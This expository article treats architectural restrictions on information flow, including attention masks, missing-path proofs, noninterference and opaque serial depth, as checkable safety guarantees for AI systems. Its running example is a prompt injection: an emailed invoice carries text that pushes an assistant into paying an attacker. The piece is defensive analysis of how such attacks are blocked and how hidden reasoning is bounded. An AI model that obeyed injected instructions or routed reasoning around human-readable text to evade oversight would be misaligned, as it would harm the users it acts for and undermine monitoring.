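# Architectural restrictions on information flow as a source of checkable safety guarantees

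## What is restricted, and what counts as a guarantee

Architectural restrictions on information flow are limits in an AI system's design on which parts of the system receive which information. A designer may prevent the model from using one stretch of text when it processes another, confine some training data to a separate module, or prevent the model that reads untrusted documents from choosing what the system does next. Safety researchers care about these limits because an outsider can sometimes check them without trusting or understanding anything the model has learned. Computer security researchers have worked on the same problem since the 1970s, and most of the vocabulary comes from their field.

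Suppose an assistant handles a person's email and can also make bank transfers. A stranger emails an invoice, and the assistant must decide whether to send money. The email may include a line addressed to the assistant rather than its owner, ordering immediate payment. A prompt injection is text in data that a model obeys as if it were an instruction from its user. The company behind the assistant could report that the assistant ignored the orders in a thousand such emails during testing, but that is weak evidence about the next email, whose author may have studied the assistant for weeks. What architecture would let an outsider check that the email cannot affect the decision?

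The simplest restriction is to have a separate program decide on payments using only the owner's instructions, without ever receiving the email. An outsider can then confirm that the email cannot influence those decisions by checking only how the components are connected. However, the assistant also cannot pay a genuine emailed invoice unless the amount and account number come from somewhere else.

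### The parts of a language model

A language model works on tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and turns each one into a vector, a list of numbers. Nearly all current models are transformers, which pass these vectors through a stack of layers. Each position in the text has a vector, called the residual stream, that every layer reads from and adds to. In a standard transformer, part of each layer processes each position separately. The other part, attention, moves information between positions, so it is the natural place to restrict information flow.

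*Heads of Security* (2026) gives the usual formula for attention. An attention head turns the residual stream at the current position into a query $q$, and turns every position it can read into a key and a value, which form the rows of the matrices $K$ and $V$. It computes weights $a = \mathrm{softmax}(qK^\top/\sqrt{d_h})$, where $d_h$ is the head's dimension, and outputs the weighted sum $aV$. The softmax makes all the weights positive and their sum one. An attention mask is a fixed rule that determines which positions each position may read. In practice, it sets the scores for forbidden positions to minus infinity before the softmax, so their weights are exactly zero. Ordinary language models already use a mask to stop each position from reading later ones.

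Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, split the attention sum at a position $c$ that matters for a decision into two parts:

$$\tilde h_c = \sum_{j \in T} \alpha_{cj} W_V h_j + \sum_{j \in U} \alpha_{cj} W_V h_j$$

Here $T$ is the set of trusted positions, $U$ the set of untrusted ones, $\alpha_{cj}$ the attention weight and $W_V h_j$ the value at position $j$. In the invoice case, $U$ holds the email, which enters the computation if any weight in the second sum is above zero. Setting those weights to zero at the deciding position is not enough, because another position may attend to the email in layer 3 and the deciding position may attend to that position in layer 4. An information path is a chain of computation steps through which one value can affect another, and a restriction has to cut every such path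 from the email to the deciding position.

Four other components can carry paths:

- The KV cache stores the keys and values of earlier positions, which later positions read during generation. If a position read the email before someone masked it, the stored entry may still carry the email's influence.
- In a mixture of experts (MoE), a router sends each token to a few of many sub-networks, called experts. The router's choice is itself information.
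- External memory is a store of documents or notes outside the network, from which the system copies items into its input. A note made from Monday's email can resurface on Friday.
- A tool call is a structured request, such as a transfer of a given sum to a given account, which ordinary software then carries out. For an assistant with access to a bank account this is the output that matters most.

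### Noninterference and labels

The property the owner wants is noninterference: changing a protected source never changes a given output. Write $s$ for the protected source, $x$ for everything else the system receives, and $F(x,s)$ for the output. Noninterference holds when

$$F(x,s) = F(x,s') \quad \text{for all } x,\ s,\ s'.$$

Language models usually pick words at random from a computed distribution, so for them $F$ has to stand for that distribution. Keeping the same outputs possible would not be enough. If an assistant might pay or refuse whatever the email contains, but pays far more often when the email is insistent, the email is influencing it.

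The term "noninterference" comes from *Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982), which models a computer as a machine that takes commands from several users and shows each user some output. A group of users does not interfere with another user if deleting the group's commands from any sequence never changes what that user sees. Deleting an input can be a stricter test than replacing it. For example, a payment decision that depended only on whether an email had arrived, and not on its wording, would pass if the email were swapped for any other but fail if it were deleted. The idea is slightly older than the name. *Language-Based Security* (Chong and Guo, 2024) traces it to Cohen's "strong dependency" of 1976, which holds when two runs that differ in only one input produce different outputs.

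Noninterference departed from the older approach, access control, which lists who may open which file. Rushby (1992), in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies*, argues that access-control rules describe a mechanism rather than an aim, so a perversely designed system can follow the rules exactly and still be obviously insecure. A noninterference claim doesn't specify a mechanism, which is why it can also be applied to neural networks, though nobody had them in mind when noninterference was defined in 1982.

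In 1976, Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* introduced a practical method for tracking flows. It gives every stored object a security class and specifies, for each class, which other classes its information may flow into. Anything computed from several objects gets the least restrictive class that covers all of them. If the only classes are confidential and unconfidential, a result computed from any confidential object is confidential. These classes are now called labels, and they record which sources may have influenced a value. Information-flow control (IFC) means labelling data by source and blocking the flows that a stated policy forbids. A later paper, *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, turned the scheme into a check that a compiler can make while analysing a program.

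Denning also saw that information can flow without anyone copying it. If b starts out nonzero and a program runs the line "if a = 0 then b := 0", anyone who reads b afterwards learns whether a was zero, even if the assignment never ran. An assistant that calls its payment tool whenever an email sounds urgent has the same kind of flow, because the email determines whether the call happens even though none of its text appears in the call.

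Labels are conservative, which quickly becomes a drawback in a transformer. With only the usual causal mask, every position after the email can attend to it in the first layer, so every later position must carry the email's label from then on, even if it took in nothing significant. Goguen and Meseguer similarly complained that flow analysis in general left the analyst with many cases that could never occur.

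Real systems need exceptions. A shop has to print the last four digits of a card number, and an assistant has to act on some invoices. A deliberate, stated exception that lets restricted information through is called a declassification. The equivalent for trust labels is an endorsement, as when the owner reads an invoice and approves it. Exceptions proved hard to formalise even for systems far simpler than a language model. Rushby recounts that Goguen and Meseguer's first method for flows that must pass through a designated component was incorrect, which they recognised in their second paper. Haigh and Young then gave a satisfactory definition, but Rushby argued that their theorem for verifying it was also wrong, and he used a machine to check the replacement.

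### Confidentiality and integrity

Noninterference can protect confidentiality, by keeping secrets from people who should not have them, or integrity, by keeping untrustworthy information from influencing things that ought to be reliable. MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), Biba's report for the US Air Force, observed that "security" had until then meant control over who may observe information, and set out to cover who may modify it as well. The invoice case is about integrity, because the worry is that the email causes the payment, not that the payment reveals what the email contained. If the assistant sent the owner's bank statement to the stranger, that would breach confidentiality.

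Confidentiality and integrity guarantees have the same form but require different restrictions on information flow. A lecture in Purdue University's *Access Control* course points out that a program must read a secret before it can leak it, whereas it can introduce bad data without reading anything. Withholding a bank statement from a module therefore prevents the module from leaking it, but withholding an untrusted email doesn't prevent the module from paying the wrong account by mistake. Under MITRE's definition, a component has integrity if it continues to behave as its creator intended. The definition allows for such mistakes by assuming that someone verified the component at the start, which is a large assumption for a trained network.

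Integrity concerns data as well as instructions. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, describe an agent (a model that carries out tasks with tools) that retrieves an invoice containing an attacker's account number on Monday and stores the details. On Tuesday the user asks it to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". Even if the agent ignores every command hidden in the invoice and takes exactly the steps the user wanted, the money goes to the attacker. A design may therefore guarantee that the invoice cannot change which steps the agent takes without guaranteeing that it cannot change where the money goes.

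### Four sources and the outputs they must not reach

The most familiar restriction limits how part of the input can affect an output. In an agent, the protected output is the choice of tool calls, their arguments, or both. In a classifier that combines many votes, it is most of the votes. If each voter sees only a small piece of an image, an attacker who alters one patch can affect only a few votes.

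Another user's request is a less obvious source. Providers run many people's requests on the same hardware at once and sometimes reuse stored computation between them, so one customer's text can affect another's answer through paths that nobody designed. The protected output is the second customer's answer, and its timing may need protection too. Many definitions leave timing out. Denning, for example, set aside "covert" channels such as a process's effect on system load.

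When the restricted information is training data, the output it must not influence is any answer given to a person who has no right to that data. *Information Flow Control in Machine Learning through Modular Model Architecture* (Tiwari, Gururangan and colleagues, 2023) divides a training set into security domains and gives each user a list of permitted ones. Its definition compares two models trained on datasets that agree on the permitted domains but may differ elsewhere. For every query, the two models must produce the same distribution over outputs. An outsider can hardly test this, since each comparison needs another training run, so the argument has to come from the design. Tiwari and colleagues train one expert per domain and activate only those for the user's permitted domains. They also rule out a router trained on the whole dataset, because its choice of experts could reveal data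 from the forbidden domains. Differential privacy, the better-known protection for training data, guarantees only that outputs stay similar whether or not the sensitive data was included, and a parameter sets how similar. The data can also be kept out of the weights, in an external memory under ordinary access control.

The model's own intermediate results differ from the other restricted flows because nobody wants to block them entirely. The aim is to keep long chains of reasoning from reaching the answer without passing through text that a person can read. The relevant measure is opaque serial depth, the length of the longest chain of computation a model can run without a human-readable intermediate step. *Quantifying the Necessity of Chain of Thought through Opaque Serial Depth* (2026) shows how to calculate an upper bound on it from the network's operations. In *An Operationalization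 of Opaque Serial Depth*, Sheffield, Westover and colleagues (2026) propose a version that anyone can determine before training from the architecture, training recipe and deployment configuration. Such a bound limits how much serial computation can be hidden, which is a weaker guarantee than noninterference and gives no information about what the hidden steps contain.

### Construction, training and test scores

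A guarantee by construction is a property that follows from how a system's components are connected, whatever weights training produces. Chong and van der Meyden (2014), in *Using Architecture to Reason About Information Security*, prove properties of this kind for conventional systems. Their results hold for every system that complies with a graph of permitted information flows, as long as a few trusted components meet additional conditions. The checker does not need to inspect the internals of the other components.

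A tendency learned in training, however strong, differs in kind from an architectural guarantee. Developers can train a model to treat text after a certain marker as data, not commands, but the marker is made of tokens, and an attacker can often type something close enough to it. Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, compare this problem to command injection in databases, where the lasting fix was to send commands and values through separate channels. They state as a theorem that an attacker can fool any method that separates commands from data by content alone, though their proof is only a sketch and relies heavily on the database analogy.

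Pant and colleagues are more exact. If $P_T$ and $P_U$ are the distributions of internal vectors that come from trusted and untrusted text, and both kinds are equally common, then the best possible guess about a vector's origin is wrong with probability

$$\tfrac{1}{2}\bigl(1 - \mathrm{TV}(P_T, P_U)\bigr),$$

where TV, the total variation distance, equals one only when the distributions do not overlap at all. For single tokens the overlap is certain, since the word "please" gets the same vector whoever wrote it. For vectors deeper in the network, which have taken in context, Pant and colleagues assume the overlap. The result is therefore a good reason not to expect a guarantee from training. It does not establish that every trained model will fail.

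Changing the architecture is not enough for a guarantee by construction. *Origin Is All You Need* (2026) gives each token an origin tag and adds a bias that strongly suppresses attention from the assistant's positions to untrusted text. This may work well, but any finite bias leaves a small positive attention weight after the softmax, and only a true mask makes that weight zero.

A good test score is a third kind of evidence, a count of how often particular attacks failed. Pant and colleagues cite an attack spread over several turns of conversation that succeeded 54.2% of the time against circuit breakers, a well-regarded defence that acts on a model's internal representations. Still, tests can cover behaviour that proofs do not. Bhattarai and Vu distinguish authorization security, which means that forbidden actions do not happen, from overall safety, because a user with permission to send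 email can send a harmful one without violating any restriction on flows.

### Three questions for each kind of evidence

The evidence on these restrictions ranges from theorems to attack tests, and the same three questions apply to all of it. What exactly is guaranteed, and for which source and output? Who can check the guarantee, and how? How much does the restriction reduce task performance or increase computation? We call this reduction or increase the capability cost.

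Anyone with the source code can see a mask, but a customer who uses the model over the internet sees only its answers and has to rely on the developer or an auditor to confirm that the mask is there. Goguen and Meseguer warned that after verifying a design, someone must also verify that the running code matches it.

In SPA, the system that Girrens and Wang built for cases like the Monday invoice, a planning model writes a complete plan before any tool runs. A separate checker then follows labels through the plan and rejects it if low-integrity data would drive an action that requires higher-integrity data. The guarantee depends on the deployer setting the labels and tool policies correctly, but the deployer can review those, and the checker's rules, without examining the planning model's weights. Turning on the label checks reduced the share of tasks completed on AgentDojo, a benchmark for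 agents under prompt injection, from 53.0% to 29.0%. Girrens and Wang attribute most of the drop to plans that passed outside data to sensitive actions, as paying an emailed invoice requires.

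## What can be proved from a missing path

Most guarantees by construction rest on one theorem about graphs. A model's computation can be drawn as a graph, with a node for each value the model computes and an arrow from that value to every value calculated directly from it. If no path of arrows leads from a source to an output, the output does not depend on the source, whatever weights training produces. In the invoice case, the source is the stranger's email and the output is the decision to pay.

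### The theorem and its proof

Run the model twice with the same weights, changing only the email. Consider the decision together with every node from which a path leads to it. The email is not one of these nodes, and any other inputs among them are the same in both runs. Each remaining node $v$ computes

$$v = f_v(p_1,\dots,p_k;\theta),$$

where $p_1,\dots,p_k$ are the values that feed directly into it and $\theta$ stands for the weights. Those values also have paths to the decision, through $v$. Now go through the nodes in the order in which the model computes them. At each one, the values feeding in have already turned out equal in the two runs, so $v$ is equal too. The decision comes last, and it is therefore the same in both runs. The argument never uses what $f_v$ computes or what $\theta$ contains.

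If the model picks its words at random, we can treat the random numbers as one more input, drawn independently of the email. Any fixed set of random numbers gives the same decision in both runs, so the distribution of decisions is also the same.

Machine-learning researchers have used this argument for at least a decade. *MADE* (2015) makes a network predict each variable from the earlier ones only, by deleting connections until no path leads to the prediction from the variable itself or any later one. Multiplying the matrices that record the remaining connections gives the number of paths from each input to each output, and a zero means that the output cannot depend on the input. *Structured Neural Networks for Density Estimation and Causal Inference* (2023) extends the method from simple orderings to arbitrary patterns of dependence.

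The graph has to include every way one value can affect another, and omissions are one reason supposedly masked text still leaks in practice. If a router chooses experts based on the email, the graph needs an arrow from that choice to everything the experts compute. If the developer trained the model on the email, the email affects $\theta$ and the two runs no longer share their weights. And if the owner reads the email before typing an instruction, the email can influence the instruction through the owner, whom the graph leaves out.

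Checking for a path is a graph search that starts at the output, follows the arrows backwards and marks each node on the way. If the search runs out of arrows without reaching the source, there is no path. The search follows each arrow at most once, so its running time grows in proportion to the size of the graph, and it needs no access to the weights.

For a transformer, one node per position and layer is enough, because only attention moves information between positions. Yang (2026), in *Post-Boundary Bridge*, a study of cheaper attention patterns, writes the search as a recursion:

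$$R_0(t)=\{t\},\qquad R_{\ell+1}(t)=R_\ell(t)\,\cup\bigcup_{s\in A_{\ell+1}(t)}R_\ell(s).$$

Here $A_\ell(t)$ is the set of positions that position $t$ may read in layer $\ell$, and $R_\ell(t)$ is the set of input positions that can affect $t$ after $\ell$ layers. The first term on the right accounts for the residual stream, which carries each position's own contents forward. Training cannot add an input position to $R_\ell(t)$, though it may leave a permitted path unused.

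Yang also tested the result on a trained model of about 200 million parameters in which each position could read only its own block of 128 tokens. The model had to identify which of four tokens had appeared at an earlier position. Yang asked each question four times, with a different token as the right answer each time. On the 1,280 groups of questions where no path led from the earlier position, accuracy was exactly 25%, because a model that receives no information from that position gives the same answer all four times and is right once. Changing the token there shifted the log-probability of the correct answer by less than $10^{-8}$ on average. A test like this can catch code that applies a mask incorrectly, but it cannot replace the proof.

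### A mask that leaks at the second layer

A small example shows how depth can open a path around a mask. Take four positions: trusted text $S$, untrusted text $U$, a summary $M$ and an answer $A$. The mask lets $A$ attend to $S$ and $M$ but not $U$, and lets $M$ attend to both $S$ and $U$. Suppose for now that $M$ starts as a fixed placeholder token, which the model fills with information as it runs.

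In the matrix $B$ below, rows are readers and columns are positions, both in the order $S, U, M, A$. An entry is one if the reader may read that position. The diagonal is all ones because of the residual stream.

$$B=\begin{pmatrix}1&0&0&0\\0&1&0&0\\1&1&1&0\\1&0&1&1\end{pmatrix}$$

With one attention layer, the bottom row lists every position that can affect $A$, and the entry for $U$ is zero. The answer does read the summary position $M$, but at that stage $M$ holds only the placeholder. So $A$ is independent of $U$ for any weights.

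For deeper models, Li and Guo (2026), in *Hasse Diagrams for Attention*, show that the reach of $L$ layers with the same mask is the $L$-th Boolean power of its matrix. Boolean multiplication follows the usual rule for matrices, with "and" ($\wedge$) in place of times and "or" ($\vee$) in place of plus. Two layers give

$$B^2=\begin{pmatrix}1&0&0&0\\0&1&0&0\\1&1&1&0\\1&1&1&1\end{pmatrix}.$$

The entry for $A$ and $U$ has changed to one because $M$ reads $U$ in the first layer and $A$ reads $M$ in the second. This path makes the third term one in the entry's expansion, $(1\wedge 0)\vee(0\wedge 1)\vee(1\wedge 1)\vee(1\wedge 0)$.

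A toy network makes the dependence visible. Let each position hold a single number, and let each layer add to it the numbers at the other positions it may read. After one layer the summary holds $M+S+U$ and the answer holds $A+S+M$. After two layers the answer holds

$$A+3S+2M+U.$$

The untrusted number is now part of the answer, although $A$ never read $U$. The coefficients count the paths from each position, and multiplying $B$ by itself in the ordinary way gives the same coefficients.

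Li and Guo prove that extra layers can only add paths and that the matrix eventually stops changing. If $B^2=B$, no amount of depth adds a path, so a designer can test a mask by squaring it. The mask above passes if the designer stops $A$ from reading $M$, or stops $M$ from reading $U$. But then either the answer can't use the summary, or the summary contains nothing from the email. No mask can let the answer use a summary of the email while keeping the answer independent of the email.

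### How far stacked windows reach

Many current models save memory with sliding-window attention, in which each position reads only the last $w$ positions, including itself. A window may look like a form of isolation, since an email 500 tokens back lies outside a window of 128. But one layer reaches back $w-1$ steps, and each further layer can add another $w-1$. After $L$ layers a position can depend on

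$$L(w-1)+1$$

input positions, counting itself, or on the whole preceding text if that is shorter. *LT2* (2026) proves this by induction for a model that runs the same layer repeatedly. After the last pass, a position depends on states up to $w-1$ steps back, and each of those already reaches $(L-1)(w-1)$ steps further. Yang trained a 20-layer model with a window of 128, which comes to 2,541 positions. Distance alone would protect a decision in that model only if the whole email came at least 2,541 positions earlier.

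A single layer of full attention removes even that protection, because its output at each position can depend on all the text before it. *InfiX-V1* (2026) describes a model that begins with a full-attention layer and places another after every three window layers. Each window layer therefore works on vectors that have already drawn on all the preceding text, so its windows save computation and memory but don't prevent earlier text from influencing later positions.

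### Stored states and generated text

Models produce text one token at a time, so the graph has to cover the whole run. The KV cache adds arrows from earlier steps to later ones. In *Thinking Outside the Box*, DeLise and Cromelin (2026) measured how much information travels along these arrows. They limited the caches of five open models to the latest 512 positions, hid a code in the text, and had each model pick the code from four candidates after the cache had dropped the code's own entry. Mistral 7B still chose correctly in 97% of trials and Muse Glimmer in all of them, because the cached entries of later positions carried the code forward. Qwen2.5 0.5B was correct in 32%, close to the 25% expected from guessing. When they instead recomputed the last 512 positions from the raw tokens, accuracy across the five models averaged 24.4% once the code fell outside those positions.

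All five models had a path from the code to the answer, but they used it to very different degrees. DeLise and Cromelin stress that a path makes dependence possible, but only measurement can establish how much information passes along it.

Generated text adds another arrow, from the model's output at one position to its input at the next. In a window model, this removes the limit of $L(w-1)$ steps, because the model can copy a detail from the email into its own text and later copy it again. The extra arrow also breaks the one-layer guarantee in the four-position example. If the model writes the summary itself after reading $U$, the words at $M$ depend on $U$, and an answer that reads those words can depend on $U$ too.

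A weaker guarantee still holds in a one-layer model: once the words of the summary are fixed, changing the email cannot change the answer. In a deeper model, this holds only if the system recomputes the vectors at $M$ from the summary's words with the email masked, because the stored vectors may carry information from the email that the words do not. Everything the email contributes to the answer then has to pass through text that a person or a program can inspect.

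### Checking a trained network instead

Suppose the wiring does allow a path from the email to the decision, and the developer reports that training taught the network to ignore the email. An outsider with the weights could try to prove this, but doing so is hard in general. *Security Properties of Neural Networks as Decision Problems* (Wurm, 2026) shows that deciding noninterference exactly is co-NP-complete for ReLU networks, whose units add up weighted inputs and replace negative totals with zero. If the output does depend on the protected input, there is a short proof, which consists essentially of two inputs that differ only in the protected part and give different outputs. Nobody knows of comparably short proofs of independence that work for every network, and a method that settled every case in polynomial time would prove that P equals NP.

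Wurm shows that the problem is no harder than this by running two copies of the network that share unprotected inputs but can have different protected ones. Noninterference holds exactly when the copies always agree, so existing software that checks whether two networks are equivalent can also check noninterference.

Wurm shows that testing a network for noninterference is at least as hard as solving a standard NP-complete problem. The problem is to decide whether some assignment of true-or-false variables meets all $m$ conditions in a list. Each condition names three variables or their negations and requires at least one of the three to hold. Wurm's network counts the conditions met, subtracts $m-1$ and replaces negative results with zero. Its output is zero everywhere if no assignment meets all the conditions, and reaches one at some input if an assignment does. When every input is protected,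 noninterference means that the output is constant, so a fast test for noninterference would solve every such problem quickly.

This is a worst-case result, and particular networks may be easy to check. The question becomes harder if the weights can change. Wurm shows that deciding whether a ReLU network stays safe under every small change to its weights, such as changes from memory faults, is complete for a class that contains co-NP and is probably larger. The missing-path theorem holds however much the weights change, as long as the mask stays in place.

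Wurm also calls exact noninterference "the wrong specification for a trained model". Any dependence on the protected input, however small, violates it. If that input correlated with anything useful in the training data, the network will depend on it at least slightly and will fail, usually by a margin too small to matter. This objection does not apply to a network with no path, because its dependence is exactly zero.

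For trained networks, Wurm proposes a version with a tolerance $\delta$. Given two groups of inputs, for example those with and without some private attribute, it requires every output from one group to lie within $\delta$ of some output from the other. Because the definition combines "for every input" with "there exists an input", the problem moves up a level in a hierarchy of complexity classes. Wurm proves that the problem is no higher than this level and conjectures that it is complete for the level.

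That version suits an audit of what outputs reveal about groups, but it is too weak for the invoice case. Consider a network that outputs $x$ when the protected input is 0 and $1-x$ when it is 1, where $x$ can be anything from 0 to 1. Both groups produce the same set of outputs, so the network passes with $\delta=0$, even though flipping the protected input changes almost every output. A better requirement would compare outputs in pairs,

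$$|F(x,s)-F(x,s')|\le\delta\quad\text{for all }x,\ s,\ s'.$$

This condition uses only "for all" quantifiers, so the problem of checking it is in co-NP, by a general lemma in Wurm's paper. A trained network could plausibly meet the condition. But when a score determines whether a payment is made, even a tiny change can matter if the score is close to the threshold.

The graph search avoids this difficulty by checking only whether a path exists. It is sound, meaning that if there is no path, the output is always independent of the input. It is also incomplete, because the output may be independent even when there is a path. Training may have set the weights along the path to zero, or two paths may cancel, as in a node that computes $s-s$. The search is much better at determining whether *any* weights could create a dependence. In the toy network above, every path adds a positive amount to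 the answer, so if an architecture's weights can imitate that network, a path always means that some weights produce a dependence.

A designer who finds a path can remove it rather than try to prove that the network ignores it. Wurm describes a similar remedy for networks whose output, such as a credit-risk score, must never fall when a given input rises. If the architecture guarantees this by its form, the designer can confirm it by simple inspection instead of a co-NP-complete check.

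### Letting filtered information through

Chong and van der Meyden show what an outsider can still prove about a system that must let some information pass. In their diagrams of permitted flows, an arrow between two components can carry a filter, a function whose output is the only information allowed across. The trusted components are the ones that apply these filters. The diagram and filters limit the information each component may have after any sequence of events. A system complies if what each component observes depends only on information within that limit.

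Chong and van der Meyden give the example of the Starlight Interactive Link, a device that lets one keyboard serve both a secret and a public network. A switch determines which network receives the keystrokes. A filter allows the public network to receive information about each flip of the switch and about keystrokes typed while the public network is selected. They prove that in every system that complies with this architecture, no information about activity on the secret network, or about keystrokes meant for it, reaches the public network.

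In a second example, a component releases some of an agency's confidential records to the public but must never reveal the activities of covert employees. Its filter lets out only information the component would have had if the covert employees had been cut off from the system. Chong and van der Meyden prove from this condition on one component that the public never learns anything about those employees' actions. The condition is hard to meet because the agency's store mixes covert records with ordinary ones, and the component must keep every trace of the covert records out of the ordinary ones.

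Compliance with the architecture diagram can be reduced to checks on an actual machine. One check uses a table of which components may read and write each stored object, which the machine must enforce. Wherever one component can write something that another can read, the diagram must have an arrow between them. The trusted components also need two local proofs. When the filter lets nothing through, the component's action must leave everything the receiver can read unchanged. When the filter gives the same output on two occasions, the action must have the same effect on any object that started out the same.

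In the invoice case, an untrusted model could read the email, and a few lines of ordinary code could filter its output. If the code provably passes on only "invoice" or "no invoice", the email's influence is limited to one bit per message, provided that timing and the number of messages carry no extra information. This guarantee doesn't require verifying the model's weights, but the attacker still chooses the bit.

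Programmers can make similar checks on the software around a model. *The Duality of Information Flow* (Gouni, Pfenning and Aldrich, 2026) presents a type system, which is a set of rules that a compiler applies before a program runs. Its types record what each value depends on and what it must not depend on. In one example, the programmer marks a neural network as off limits to untrusted data, and the compiler rejects a line that passes user input to it. The types can also express controlled releases of information, and the paper proves full noninterference for the resulting language. Researchers had long assumed that practical programs need exceptions that weaken noninterference. The proof assistant Lean checked the proofs.

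### From independence to safety

Chong and van der Meyden also give the example of an election, in which voters send ballots to an authority that publishes the results. They prove that votes stay anonymous if the authority satisfies one condition, that the results would be the same if voters exchanged ballots among themselves. If Alice thinks it possible that Bob chose the first candidate and Charlie the second, she must also think the reverse possible. The condition does not guarantee a correct count, which they treat as a separate requirement. An authority that always announced the same winner, regardless of the ballots, would still satisfy the anonymity condition.

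The missing-path theorem holds for all weights, including random ones and weights that make the payment program approve every request. A missing path alone therefore cannot guarantee that the program makes good use of the information it does receive.

Independence does make other evidence go further. Let $D(s,u)$ be the decision when the owner's instructions are $s$ and the email is $u$. If a tester finds that the decision is acceptable with one email $u_0$, then

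$$D(s,u)=D(s,u_0)\quad\text{for every }u,$$

and no attacker can find an email that changes it. The tester still has to try many different instructions, but those come from the owner, who is not trying to defeat the test.

This reasoning assumes that the email does not affect which decision is acceptable. Suppose the real supplier emails to warn that a thief has taken over the account named in the owner's instructions. The payment program will ignore this warning just as it would ignore an attacker's email, and will pay the thief. Yang proves that if $K$ answers are equally likely, and only a source with no path to the output reveals which is right, accuracy cannot exceed $1/K$. When only the email can settle whether to pay or wait, and both are equally likely to be right, training cannot raise the program's accuracy above 50%.

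## Bounds on reasoning that is not written down

The missing-path theorem depends only on whether a path exists, but the length of paths also matters because it limits how much step-by-step reasoning a model can do before it has to write something down. Many language models work through hard problems in a chain of thought, which is text the model writes before its answer. A person can read that text, unlike the vectors inside the network.

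In a standard transformer, layer 5 at any position works only on what layer 4 produced at that position and earlier ones. Each step in a chain of dependent calculations therefore has to happen in a higher layer than the step before it. After the last layer, the model chooses a token, which enters the network again at the first layer. Later computation in the lower layers can use the results of higher layers only through these tokens. The KV cache doesn't provide another route, because only layer 5 at later positions reads the entries that layer 5 stored. A chain with more steps than one pass through the layers can hold therefore has to pass through written text.

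It is harder to say which tasks need such a chain. Suppose each of many boxes contains the number of another box, and the task is to follow the trail for 1,000 steps. A network could work out where the trail leads after two steps from every box at once, combine those results to cover four steps, then eight, and finish in about ten rounds. Complexity theorists believe that some problems have no such shortcut. *Quantifying the Necessity of Chain of Thought through Opaque Serial Depth* gives the example of planning in Markov decision processes, a standard model of choosing actions when outcomes are partly random. But this belief rests on unproved conjectures about how difficulty grows with the size of the problem, so we can't use it to determine which tasks will require a particular model to write down its reasoning.

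### Defining the depth

Counting layers is a crude way to measure depth, since designers disagree about what a layer is. Brown-Cohen, Lindner and Shah, who wrote the paper, use circuits instead. A circuit breaks a calculation into gates, each of which either combines two numbers, for example by adding or multiplying them, or applies a simple function to one number. The depth of a network that computes the function $f$ is

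$$\mathrm{Depth}(f)=\min_{C}\ \max_{P \text{ in } C}\ \mathrm{length}(P),$$

where $C$ ranges over the circuits that compute $f$ and $P$ over the paths from an input to an output. The size of $C$ may grow only polynomially with the number of parameters. Without that limit, a gigantic lookup table of answers would count as a shallow circuit for almost anything.

Next, someone marks a set $R$ of nodes as readable. For each node $u$ in $R$, let $f^u$ be the function that computes $u$ from the nearest readable nodes before it. Opaque serial depth is the largest depth between readable nodes:

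$$\max_{u\in R}\ \mathrm{Depth}(f^u).$$

In an ordinary language model, $R$ contains every token of the prompt and every token the model writes. The opaque serial depth is therefore the depth of a single pass through the network, however long the output is.

### Computing an upper bound

Finding the shallowest possible circuit is probably intractable, but any circuit that computes the function gives an upper bound on the minimum depth, and the network's code describes one such circuit. The algorithm runs the same backward search as the missing-path check, but starts from each readable node and adds up the depth of the operations until it reaches another readable node. Adding $n$ numbers takes $\lceil\log_2 n\rceil$ steps, because a circuit can add them in pairs, then add the results in pairs, and so on.

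A network with one input, two layers of four ReLU units and one output takes nine steps. The first layer takes two steps, one to multiply and one to apply the ReLU. The second takes four, because it must also add four numbers, which takes two steps. The output takes three, because it multiplies and adds four numbers but doesn't apply a ReLU.

Brown-Cohen and colleagues automated this for networks written in JAX, a library for numerical computing. Their tool assigns a depth to each elementary operation in the program, and about 75 kinds of operation were enough for Google's Gemma 3 models. It runs in seconds and doesn't need trained weights. They also worked out tighter bounds by hand for the longest text each model accepts:

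| Model | Layers | Bound by hand | Bound from the tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 3 1B | 26 | 4,490 | 5,728 |
| Gemma 3 4B | 34 | 6,206 | 7,958 |
| Gemma 3 12B | 48 | 8,754 | 11,268 |
| Gemma 3 27B | 62 | 11,662 | 14,856 |

The tool's bound is about 28% higher than the hand-derived one because the tool misses some simplifications, such as folding a final addition into a sum the network already computes. Text length has little effect on the bound. For the smallest model, the hand-derived bound is $4370+8\log_2 T$ steps for a text of $T$ tokens, so doubling the text adds eight steps.

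Mixture-of-experts (MoE) models should have lower depth than dense models with the same number of parameters, because experts run in parallel and adding more doesn't lengthen the path. The tool gave a depth of 4,096 for an MoE model with 91 billion parameters, 11 billion of them active for each token, and 11,268 for the dense Gemma 3 12B. But the MoE model also had fewer layers (28 against 48) and a shorter text (512 tokens against 128,000). By the hand calculation, the shorter text accounts for only about 200 steps of the difference, and the number of layers probably explains much more.

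For the newer Gemma 4 models, *How Transparent is DiffusionGemma?* (Engels, McDougall and colleagues, 2026) reports a higher depth from the tool for the MoE model, Gemma 4 26B A4B (21,235), than for the dense Gemma 4 31B (13,750). The paper attributes this anomaly to code that sorts tokens by expert for efficiency and then restores their order. The tool counts the sorting, even though the sorting adds no real depth.

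### One model with two depths

DiffusionGemma, which Google DeepMind built from Gemma 4 26B A4B, starts with a block of 256 random tokens, called a canvas, and revises the whole block in up to 48 steps instead of writing one token after another. Each step passes the current tokens and one extra vector per position to the next step. That vector is an average of the vectors for every token in the vocabulary, weighted by the probability the model currently gives each token.

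If these extra vectors are unreadable, a hidden chain can run through all 48 steps, and the tool's bound is 608,016, or 28.6 times the figure for Gemma 4 26B A4B. If a person can read everything that passes between steps, the longest hidden chain covers only one step. The bound is then 23,571, or 1.1 times Gemma's. The two figures fit a fixed cost for each further step:

$$608{,}016 = 23{,}571 + 47\times 12{,}435.$$

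In practice the model usually stops after 12 to 16 steps. By the same arithmetic, its bound with unreadable vectors is between 160,356 and 210,096, still roughly eight to ten times Gemma's. All of these figures are upper bounds, so the ratios between the true depths could differ.

The network is the same for both the high and low figures, so the result depends on whether the vectors are readable. To test this, Engels and colleagues kept only the tokens with a probability of at least 3% at each position and spread the remaining probability evenly over the rest of the vocabulary. The model did as well as before on tests of coding, mathematics and science. They then examined the tokens that survived the cut on 800 prompts from real users. Even in the first steps, more than 85% of these tokens matched or resembled a token that ended up at that position or within ten positions of it.

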